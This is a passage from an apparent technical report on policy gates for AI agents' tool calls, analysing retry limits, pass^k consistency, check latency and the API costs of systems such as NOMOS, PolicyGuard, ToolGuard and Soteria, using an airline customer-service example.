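From the third attempt on, a bad call is more likely to run than a good one. Raising the limit from three attempts to ten would increase the share of tasks ending in a good call from 49.0% to 49.4%, and the share ending in a bad call from 7.7% to 20.7%. An agent that keeps sending the same rejected call does less damage, because a deterministic gate refuses it every time, but an agent under an attacker's influence may vary its calls on purpose.

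### When to hand over to a person

Let *v* be the benefit if the agent completes the task itself instead of passing it to a person now, *h* the harm of a bad call, and *c* the cost of one more attempt. Another attempt is worthwhile if

$$P(\text{good}) \cdot v > P(\text{bad}) \cdot h + c.$$

If we ignore *c*, the first attempt in the table is worthwhile when the harm from a bad call is less than about 13 times the benefit of a good one. The limit falls to 3.1 times for the second attempt and 0.6 times for the third. Cancelling a ticket that a customer wanted to keep is probably much worse than using a few minutes of a staff member's time. If it is five times worse, the airline should hand over to staff after the first refusal.

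If no bad call can pass the gate, the only drawback of another attempt is the resources it uses, *c*. When *c* is 5% of *v*, a second attempt is worthwhile but a third is not. In this example the odds of success fall after every refusal, so the chance to try again later never justifies an attempt that isn't worthwhile by itself.

The airline can replace these invented numbers with rates from its own logs by counting how often the next attempt succeeded after one refusal, after two, and so on. It should count separately for each rule, because a missing confirmation is much easier to fix than a booking that is too old. If the check shows that no further attempt could succeed, the gate should stop the attempts immediately. The count of refusals can restart when a fact that the gate checks has changed, such as when the customer confirms, but not when the model only rewords its request.

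### How much real retries help

In *Quantitative Certification of Agentic Tool Selection* (2025), Llama-3.1 had to choose a suitable tool from a list with distractors. Its estimated success rate (an upper bound) was 50% without a retry and 57% with one. The retry fixed only about one in seven of the failed choices; if the attempts had been independent, the rate would have been 75%. Removing the failed tool from the list before the retry raised the rate to 63%, and two retries with the tool's output in view raised it to 70%. The paper does not count retries on destructive calls, because a better choice afterwards can't undo a leaked password.

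Soteria's planner can retry more safely because it makes its attempts before any tool runs. In tests by He and colleagues, which allowed up to eight retries, 23.3% of the 60 plans written as one piece passed verification on the first attempt. If the nine attempts were independent, about 54 plans would eventually have passed, but 38 did. Of the 68 plans that reuse sub-plans, 48.5% passed on the first attempt. The same calculation predicts that nearly all of them would eventually pass, and 65 did.

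The difference is consistent with the kinds of error involved. Syntax errors are the main kind left in plans with sub-plans, and as a model corrects them, each attempt may start closer to success than the one before. But if a model left out the flown-status check because it misinterpreted the policy, it will probably do so again on the next attempt.

The number of retries allowed may also affect how many tasks get completed. Soteria completed 60.0% of airline tasks with eight planning retries and averaged 50.8% with three. The first figure comes from a single run and the second from five, so chance may explain part of the gap. Soteria broke no formal rules in either setup, so allowing fewer retries seems to reduce task completion but not safety.

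Whole tasks show the same pattern as single calls. In *Built on Broken Assumptions (BOBA)* (2026), coding agents attempted each chain of 20 requests eight times. Depending on the model, they completed 39% to 67% of the chains per attempt on average. If all chains were equally hard and the attempts were independent, even the weakest model would have completed about 98% of the chains at least once. The models actually completed 60% to 84% at least once, and every model failed the same 19 chains on every attempt.

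Switching to a different model may not help much either. When two models both failed somewhere in a chain, their first failures fell on the same request in 44.6% of cases, compared with 5.4% expected if the positions were independent.

A failed attempt can also make the next one more likely to fail. *Why Retrying Fails* (2026) models an agent whose error rate per step rises when an earlier failure is still in its context. If the rate rises from 5% to 15%, for example, the chance of completing ten steps falls from 60% to 20%. A host can avoid this by deleting the refused call from the context before the model tries again, as Agent-C does with open models.

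### Agents that keep trying

The model is a poor choice for deciding when to stop retrying. In *Tool-Calling LLM Agents Under Realistic MCP Faults*, Iannillo, Owotogbe and colleagues (2026) injected faults into tool calls made by agents using two open models, with 20 and 120 billion parameters. Most of the faults were permanent, so calling the same tool again couldn't help. A policy refusal is similar because it lasts until a relevant fact changes.

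After a faulty call, the agents called the same tool again 21% of the time, switched to another tool 57% of the time, and made no further calls 22% of the time. In 38 of 450 runs, an agent called the same failing tool at least three times in a row, and one called it 12 times. Iannillo and colleagues also read reasoning traces from the larger model and found none in which it distinguished a permanent fault from a temporary one. The larger model handled faults no better than the smaller one.

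The agent framework had more effect on when agents gave up. With one framework, 11% of faulty calls led the agent to stop calling tools, compared with 49% with another. All three frameworks tested left retries up to the model.

Software outside the model can also retry automatically, but this helps only with temporary faults. In *Knowing When to Stop* (2026), the host repeated certain failed queries up to twice, after waits of one and two seconds. Task success did not change significantly in any of the six conditions tested. In one condition, 101 runs lost their working environment late in the task and received automatic retries. No operation in those runs succeeded after the first automatic retry.

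A limit on attempts has to be in the code and cover the right loop. Hou, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *When Agents Do Not Stop*, scanned 6,549 agent projects for loops without an effective limit and confirmed 68 in 47 projects. Seventeen of these loops were retry loops. One project, LiteRAG, requests a plan from a model and tries again whenever the plan can't be parsed or fails a check, with no limit on attempts, time or tokens. If the check in such a loop were a gate that rejected every plan, the agent would never stop.

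Only 0.7% of the projects had a confirmed loop of this kind, though the scan missed some. Hou and colleagues found seven more among the alerts from two other detection methods. Most agent frameworks offer a limit on turns, but a developer can disable it or put it outside the loop it should limit. If the airline's host retries refused calls within a single turn, the limit won't stop the retries.

A refused call never ran, so retrying it is safer than retrying a call that timed out, which may have run. *Verified Tool Calls Improve LLM Agent Reliability Under Non-Atomic Failures* (2026) found that agents that retried after an ambiguous failure without checking often repeated an action that had already succeeded. Checking the state of the external system before each retry made duplicates much less common. The formulas above apply only to refusals.

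### Success on every trial

The airline also needs the agent to handle the same request correctly every time. Pass^k measures this across separate conversations rather than retries within one.

An agent can be good at completing tasks at least once in several attempts but bad at completing them every time. In one setting of *Bank-World* (2026), a Gemini model and a Claude Opus model each attempted 25 banking tasks eight times. Gemini fully completed 19 tasks at least once but none all eight times. Opus fully completed 17 at least once and 6 all eight times. Gemini has more to gain from retries if something can detect its failures. A gate detects forbidden calls but not unfinished tasks.

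Yu and colleagues ran each airline task five times with and without NOMOS:

| | pass^1 | pass^2 | pass^3 | pass^4 | pass^5 | pass^5 / pass^1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| No gate | 39.2% | 27.4% | 23.0% | 21.2% | 20.0% | 0.51 |
| NOMOS | 47.6% | 40.6% | 37.0% | 34.4% | 32.0% | 0.67 |

The differences are statistically significant for *k* from 2 to 4, without a correction for testing several values of *k*. Each task had five trials, so pass^5 is the share of tasks that the agent solved every time. That share rose from 10 of the 50 tasks to 16.

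If all the tasks were equally hard, an agent with a pass^1 of 39.2% would have a pass^5 of about 1%. Its actual pass^5 is 20%, because the agent always solves some tasks and rarely solves others. This unevenness also makes retries less useful than the independent model predicts.

A gate can make an agent more consistent by blocking forbidden changes, which would usually leave the database in the wrong state and fail the task. After a block, the run can still end in the same state as one in which the model never proposed the change.

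NOMOS had no such effect on retail tasks, where pass^1 fell from 52.4% to 50.2% and pass^4 from 24.6% to 22.8%. Neither change is significant. Yu and colleagues attribute the declines to the sequence of the agents' actions. Retail allows only one modification per order, so an agent that changes the items first can't change the address afterwards, with or without a gate.

A model acting as judge can also achieve this consistency without formal rules. When one replaced the airline gate, pass^1 was 47.2% and pass^5 was 38.0%, neither significantly different from the result with NOMOS. With a local model as the judge, however, pass^5 fell to 16.0%, significantly below NOMOS.

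As *k* rose from 1 to 4 in the test by Winston and colleagues, pass^k fell by 26% with their solver gate and by 40% without it. Overall success was slightly higher with the gate, but the gated agent made fewer correct write calls. Winston and colleagues give no confidence intervals.

A gate can improve consistency just by refusing more changes, so a drop in correct changes is a reason for caution. If a gate refused every change, the agent would succeed every time at tasks that need no change and never at the others, and its pass^k would not fall as *k* rose. Developers should therefore read consistency together with pass^1 and the number of correct changes. On the airline tasks, NOMOS greatly reduced the number of changes, but pass^1 did not fall.

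### Errors over long tasks

The more steps a task has, the more opportunities there are for something to go wrong. The 35% chance of success that AWS's Matt Garman gave for 1,000 steps, as ITWeb reported, treats errors as independent and assumes that any single error ruins the task. If errors aren't independent, the same average rate of 0.1% can produce almost any result:

| How the errors are distributed | Chance of 1,000 steps without an error |
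|---|---|
| Independently, with a 0.1% chance at each step | 36.8% |
| One step in every task always fails | 0% |
| Every step fails in one task out of 1,000, and no step fails in the others | 99.9% |

*Grounded Scaling* (2026) makes the general point that a task can be more likely to succeed than the product of its per-step success rates implies when failures cluster in a few sessions, and less likely when they are spread more evenly than chance would produce. The coding results in *Built on Broken Assumptions (BOBA)* suggest that some steps are much harder than others. The average error rate per step is therefore a poor guide to success on whole tasks, which a company should measure directly.

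Garman's calculation also leaves out recovery. If a gate detected every error and each step allowed a second, independent attempt, only one step in a million would fail, and all 1,000 steps would succeed 99.9% of the time. If the gate caught 95% of the errors and retries always fixed those, the chance of all 1,000 steps succeeding would be about 95%. Garman's argument supports using a gate with retries, as long as the gate catches most of the errors that matter.

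A gate also adds errors when it refuses correct calls. Suppose the agent never makes a mistake, but the gate refuses 2% of correct changes, independently of one another. A task with one change then succeeds 98% of the time, a task with ten changes 82%, and a task with 50 changes 36%.

Re-prompting the model doesn't help if the rule itself is wrong, because the gate will reject the correct call every time. It can even make things worse, since any call that does pass is likely to be something the customer didn't want.

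False refusals are rarely spread evenly, though. NOMOS's rule against modifying basic economy flights also blocks cabin changes that the policy permits. When Yu and colleagues replayed successful conversations recorded without the gate, the rule blocked 15 calls, all of them attempts to change only the cabin, and 14 came from the same task. The airline would probably see one kind of request fail repeatedly while everything else worked normally, which makes the faulty rule easier to find in the logs.

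A false refusal partway through a task can leave the customer worse off than if the agent had done nothing. If the agent cancels her old flight and the gate then wrongly blocks the new booking, she has no flight, and the gate will refuse the same booking again if the agent retries it.

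## What repeated attempts cost in money and time

After a refusal, the customer waits while the model writes another call, and the airline pays for the extra tokens. The gate also adds a delay of its own to every attempt, including those that pass. If the gate accepts attempt number *N*, the time from the start of the first attempt to the tool's result is

$$T = N\,(t_{\text{model}} + t_{\text{check}}) + t_{\text{tool}}.$$

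*SARC* (2026), which proposes an architecture for governing agents, says a call to a strong model takes tens of seconds and a simple rule check takes microseconds to a few milliseconds. Model calls can be much faster. With low reasoning effort, the agents He and colleagues tested took a median of 0.6 to 1.6 seconds per turn. Even then, a rule check takes a tiny fraction of the time a retry takes.

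### How long a check takes

Published check times range from microseconds to many seconds, partly because researchers timed different things. Yu and colleagues timed only the function in NOMOS that decides whether a call may run. *AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) reports the time for a full round trip to the Aegis gateway, which searches a call's arguments for signs of an attack and then applies rules written in JSON Schema. *Sapien* (2026), which describes a policy engine for agents, reports times with and without the surrounding software.

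Some systems also use a language model as part of the check. *Agent-Sentry* (2026) decides most calls with deterministic checks and sends the rest to a model to judge. In *VIGIL* (2026), a model translates the written instructions that come with an agent's skills into formal rules, and an SMT solver checks the agent's actions against them. *PolicyGuard* has a model read the conversation before every call that would change a record.

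| Check | Time | What the time includes |
|---|---|---|
| NOMOS | 3 microseconds, mean | The decision alone, over 1,801 replayed calls |
| Sapien | Under 1 ms | The rule check alone |
| Sapien | About 15 to 45 ms | Interception by a proxy and logging |
| Aegis | 8.3 ms, median | Reading the arguments, a local network round trip, scanning and policy rules |
| AWS's AgentCore gateway | "in milliseconds" | Amazon doesn't specify |
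| Agent-Sentry, deterministic checks | Under 10 ms | All the checks in one run |
| VIGIL, solver | 0.27 s | The solver-backed check alone |
| VIGIL, everything | 4.38 s, mean | One model call to translate the rules, then the check |
| Agent-Sentry, judge | 1.2 s, mean | One model call |
| PolicyGuard | 7.9 to 19.2 s, median | One model call and the tool's own running time |

The model call accounts for 92.5% of VIGIL's 4.38 seconds, so a faster solver would barely reduce the delay. The same is probably true of Winston and colleagues' gate, which also relies on a model for its facts. *VIGIL* argues that its delay is acceptable because a coding agent's ordinary shell commands take 4 to 6 seconds on average. A customer in a chat might notice the delay more.

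The shortest times also exclude the time spent collecting facts. ToolGuard's generated code looks up records before evaluating the rules, and these lookups don't appear in the agent's transcript. *PolicyGuard* estimates from the code that each airline task requiring a change involves about seven to nine of these lookups, though the true number could be anywhere from three to 15. If each lookup took 20 milliseconds, eight of them would add 0.16 seconds to the time needed to evaluate the rules.

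Conversations averaged 21.3 seconds with NOMOS and 20.1 seconds without a gate. The gate makes each decision in microseconds, so the extra 1.2 seconds probably came from the turns that followed refusals, or from chance.

### The overhead of a model-based checker

When Yu and colleagues replaced NOMOS with their own version of PolicyGuard, the mean time for an airline run rose 74%, from 21.3 to 37.1 seconds. That is 85% longer than a run with no gate. The checker made 347 model calls in 250 runs, or only about 1.4 per run.

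The developers' own measurements show how much the overhead depends on the model:

| Agent | Model that checks | Median check | Mean task time, no gate | Mean task time, PolicyGuard |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4 | GPT-5.4 | 7.9 s | 32.4 s | 45.3 s (+40%) |
| GPT-5.4 | GPT-5.4-mini | 2.6 s | 32.4 s | 32.8 s (+1%) |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11.3 s | 38.7 s | 57.7 s (+49%) |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | Gemini 2.5 Pro | 19.2 s | 67.5 s | 112.3 s (+66%) |

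With GPT-5.4 in both roles, a task had 1.27 checks on average, each taking 7.9 seconds. The checks account for roughly 10 of the 13 extra seconds, and the rest presumably comes from the conversation after a refusal.

The smaller checker removed almost all of the overhead. Its checks alone should have added nearly three seconds, so shorter conversations or chance must have hidden some of that time. A weaker checker can also make the agent less reliable, as Yu and colleagues found with a local model.

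*SARC* argues against checks that call another model because they double the time of each step and are as unpredictable as the model they are meant to control. The added time is a weaker objection over a whole task, since PolicyGuard checks only calls that change records, and most airline tasks have one or two of those.

### A cheap check can lead to an expensive conversation

ToolGuard's checks run as ordinary code and need no model, so one would expect it to be cheaper than PolicyGuard. *PolicyGuard* reports the total API cost of 200 airline runs with each system. Dividing that total by the number of successful runs gives the cost of a success:

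| Agent | Total, no gate | Total, PolicyGuard | Total, ToolGuard | Per success, no gate | Per success, PolicyGuard | Per success, ToolGuard |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4 | $10.83 | $13.08 | $11.67 | $0.08 | $0.09 | $0.10 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | $47.07 | $50.26 | $58.76 | $0.29 | $0.30 | $0.50 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | $18.48 | $19.86 | $21.45 | $0.13 | $0.14 | $0.21 |

ToolGuard cost more than PolicyGuard with Sonnet and Gemini, even though its checks made no model calls. It refused nearly four-fifths of the changes that Sonnet attempted, and each refusal led to more conversation. On tasks that required a change, ToolGuard increased the number of messages by 19% to 28%, and PolicyGuard by 3% to 13%. Many of ToolGuard's refusals were also wrong, so fewer tasks succeeded.

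PolicyGuard's developers ran this comparison, and a stronger set of generated guards might have done better. With either system, the airline pays for more turns and completes fewer tasks when the gate refuses calls it should accept.

### How many attempts to expect

Let *p* be the probability that the gate accepts a given proposal, whether or not the call is what the customer wanted, and let *n* be the largest number of attempts allowed. If attempts are independent, the model reaches attempt *k* with probability $(1-p)^{k-1}$, and adding these probabilities gives the expected number of attempts:

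$$E[N] = \sum_{k=1}^{n}(1-p)^{k-1} = \frac{1-(1-p)^n}{p}.$$

If each proposal passes with probability *p* = 0.6 and the limit is *n* = 3 attempts, the expected number of attempts is 1 + 0.4 + 0.16 = 1.56. Without a limit it would be 1.67, so the limit has little effect on the average when most proposals pass.

A limit matters more when some requests can never succeed, because without one they would be retried forever. In the earlier example, half of all tasks can never succeed and each attempt at the others works 80% of the time, so 40% of first attempts pass. With a perfect gate and a limit of three, the expected number of attempts is 1 + 0.6 + 0.52 = 2.12.

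*Sapien* reports that after the system blocked an action, the agent resolved the problem within one retry 84% of the time. The paper also tested a fixed list of permitted tools. When that list left out a tool the agent tried to use, the agent could keep retrying until it reached a limit of 200.

### Paying for the same context again

A model has no memory between calls, so the host sends the whole context again with each attempt. Let *C* be the number of tokens in the context at the first attempt, and let *d* be the number that each refusal adds, counting both the refused call and the gate's message. Attempt *k* then has *C* + (*k* − 1)*d* input tokens, and *N* attempts have

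$$\sum_{k=1}^{N}\bigl(C+(k-1)d\bigr) = NC + \frac{dN(N-1)}{2}.$$

Suppose the airline's policy, tool descriptions and conversation take up 20,000 tokens, and each refusal adds 600. Three attempts use 20,000 + 20,600 + 21,200 = 61,800 input tokens. All but 1,800 of these come from sending the original context three times, so shortening the refusal message would save very little.

The second term grows with the square of *N*, so it becomes large if nothing stops the agent from retrying. At 200 attempts, the original context accounts for 4 million tokens and the accumulated refusals for another 11.9 million.

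Providers can reduce this cost through *prefix caching*, which reuses earlier computation on the beginning of an input if that beginning hasn't changed. If the first attempt starts with an empty cache, the host pays the full price for *C* + (*N* − 1)*d* tokens and the cached price for the rest. For three attempts, the host pays the full price for 21,200 tokens and the cached price for 40,600.

Prices vary by provider and model, so this example assumes that a million tokens cost $2 as new input, $0.20 as cached input and $10 as output. On each attempt the model writes 300 tokens of reasoning and a 200-token call. The host then drops the reasoning, so each refusal adds 600 tokens to the context, 200 from the call and 400 from the gate's message.

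| | One attempt | Three attempts, no caching | Three attempts, caching |
|---|---|---|---|
| New input tokens | 20,000 | 61,800 | 21,200 |
| Cached input tokens | 0 | 0 | 40,600 |
| Output tokens | 500 | 1,500 | 1,500 |
| Total price | $0.045 | $0.139 | $0.066 |

Caching reduces the price of the two retries from about 9 cents to 2. It also raises output's share of that price from about a tenth to half, so long reasoning before every attempt would become the main expense. If cached input cost half as much as new input instead of a tenth, the total would be 9.8 cents.

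The saving from caching depends on keeping the start of the context unchanged. Adding a refusal message at the end preserves the cache. Removing a tool from the list after a failure can help a model choose better, but it may discard most of the cache if the tool descriptions come first.

Dropping old reasoning is another way to save tokens. *Sequent-Prover* (2026) describes an agent that writes problems for Z3 and revises them after reading the solver's output. The agent's host resends the earlier calls and results on every turn but leaves out the model's earlier reasoning, so each turn adds fewer tokens to the next.

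### Why the average hides the slow cases

In the example with *p* = 0.6, suppose each attempt takes four seconds. The mean time per call is 1.56 × 4 = 6.2 seconds, but 16% of calls need a third attempt and take 12 seconds. If a task has five such calls, the chance that at least one takes 12 seconds is 1 − 0.84⁵, or 58%. A typical customer with a long request will therefore have a delay that looks unusual in single-call statistics.

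Measured times show the same pattern:

- In the test by Yu and colleagues, the model-based checker raised the mean run time by 74% compared with NOMOS, but the *95th percentile*, the time that only one run in 20 exceeds, was 2.8 times as long.
- *Agent-Sentry* reports an average delay of 0.073 seconds per run because the judge handles only 3.1% of decisions. No run actually waits 0.073 seconds for the judge. Most don't wait for it at all, and about 6% wait at least 1.2 seconds, assuming two independent decisions per run.
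- Soteria's planner took a median of 0.53 seconds per turn with GPT-5.4-mini, but 1% of turns took nearly eight seconds or more. In a conversation with ten turns, the chance of at least one such delay is about 10% if the delays are independent.

Yuan and colleagues report that 95% of Aegis's checks took at most 14.7 milliseconds and 99% took at most 23.1. These figures exclude calls that wait for a person's approval. When Aegis holds a risky call, the agent stops for up to five minutes while the software checks for a decision every two seconds. If 1% of calls waited two minutes for approval, the mean delay would rise by 1.2 seconds, while the median would stay at about 8 milliseconds.

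Averages are still useful for budgeting because the expected delays of separate calls add up, whereas percentiles don't. Twenty checks with a median of 8.3 milliseconds each will take around 0.17 seconds in total. Their combined 99th percentile will usually be well below 20 times the 23.1 milliseconds for a single check, because all twenty are unlikely to be slow at once unless they share a cause, such as an overloaded gateway. The airline should therefore measure the delay of whole conversations as well as single checks.

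### Ways to shorten the wait

Masking avoids a refusal, and so saves a whole turn, when a call's only fault would be an argument that the schema forbids. A gate may also save time by stopping a sequence early when it is bound to fail. In tests by He and colleagues, a step took a median of about one second with Soteria's monitor and 2.5 seconds without it. They attribute the difference to the agent having fewer mistakes to recover from.

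Repairing a tool call locally is far quicker than re-prompting if the repair doesn't need a language model, as with LeanGuard's search for corrected arguments. In *Autonomous Topology Mutation* (2026), a repair component took 0.11 milliseconds when the call needed no repair and 0.26 milliseconds when it did. The test used a stand-in for the language model, so a repair that needs a real model would take much longer. Local repair is suitable only if the customer would accept the changed call.

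**Compiling a policy once can save money and time over many runs.** Compiling the airline rules for NOMOS with a frontier model cost $1.02 in API fees. PolicyGuard's checks with GPT-5.4, including the extra conversation, added about 1.1 cents per run, so the compilation would pay for itself after roughly 90 runs. Sapien instead generates a new policy for every task, which takes 43 to 100 seconds on AgentDojo. This makes Sapien slower overall than the fixed list of tools, although each of its checks takes less than a millisecond.

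VIGIL can keep the rules it has compiled for each skill, which would remove most of its 4.38 seconds on later runs. A host should be more careful about caching the gate's decisions, because the same rule can give a different answer on a later call. For example, a customer has 24 hours to cancel, so the answer for reservation H4LN9P changes as the booking gets older.

If each call is limited to three attempts of four seconds each, the customer waits at most 12 seconds plus the tool's own running time. The two limits have to be chosen together because they multiply. *Sequent-Prover* allows 10 turns with up to 30 seconds of solver time in each, so a run within both limits could still spend five minutes in the solver.

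### What Soteria's plans cost

Soteria verifies a plan before any tool runs, which should prevent failed attempts later. He and colleagues report the average API price per task. The last two columns show that price divided by the share of tasks the agent completed without a violation.

| Model and benchmark | Per task, no gate | Per task, Soteria | Per success, no gate | Per success, Soteria |
|---|---|---|---|---|
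| GPT-5.4-mini, airline | $0.031 | $0.125 | $0.09 | $0.21 |
| GPT-5.4-mini, retail | $0.036 | $0.154 | $0.18 | $0.44 |
| GPT-5.4-mini, Toolathlon | $0.045 | $0.033 | $1.94 | $0.28 |
| Claude Opus 4.6, airline | $0.318 | $0.796 | $0.61 | $0.90 |
| Claude Opus 4.6, retail | $0.370 | $0.640 | $0.80 | $0.71 |
| Claude Opus 4.6, Toolathlon | $0.972 | $0.431 | $8.36 | $2.32 |

Running GPT-5.4-mini on airline tasks costs four times as much with Soteria as with no gate, but running Opus on Toolathlon costs less than half as much with Soteria. The difference comes mainly from the number of plans Soteria writes. Airline and retail customers reveal what they want over several messages, and Soteria writes a new plan after each one. A Toolathlon task is a single request, so it needs only one plan, which can save the agent effort over a long series of steps.

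Most of the extra cost on airline tasks comes from writing plans. With GPT-5.4-mini, adding an unverified plan raised the cost per task from $0.031 to $0.102. Verification and its retries raised it to $0.150. The complete system, with reusable sub-plans and the monitor, cost $0.125. The monitor costs almost nothing to run because it doesn't use a solver.

Some of the saving on Toolathlon may come from doing less work. Gemini 3 Flash wrote to files 281 times without a gate and 62 times with Soteria, while the number of reads hardly changed. Opus also completed fewer tasks with Soteria if violations are ignored. Counted that way, a completed task cost $3.22 without a gate and $2.32 with Soteria, a much smaller saving than the table shows. The Toolathlon figures are also rough because they depend on so few successes, with only one for GPT-5.4-mini without a gate.

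A plain monitor may be better value for a cheap model. GPT-5.4-mini with AgentSpec cost $0.032 per airline task and completed half of the 50 tasks without a violation. That is about 6 cents per success, less than with Soteria or with no gate. However, AgentSpec let through eight violations on those tasks, while Soteria let through none.

For Opus on airline tasks, Soteria added 48 cents per task and raised the success rate from 52% to 88%, so each additional success cost about $1.33. An airline would probably pay an employee more than that to take over a failed conversation. The $1.33 excludes the few hours that He and colleagues spent formalizing and checking each benchmark's rules, but the airline could spread that work over every conversation until its policy changes.
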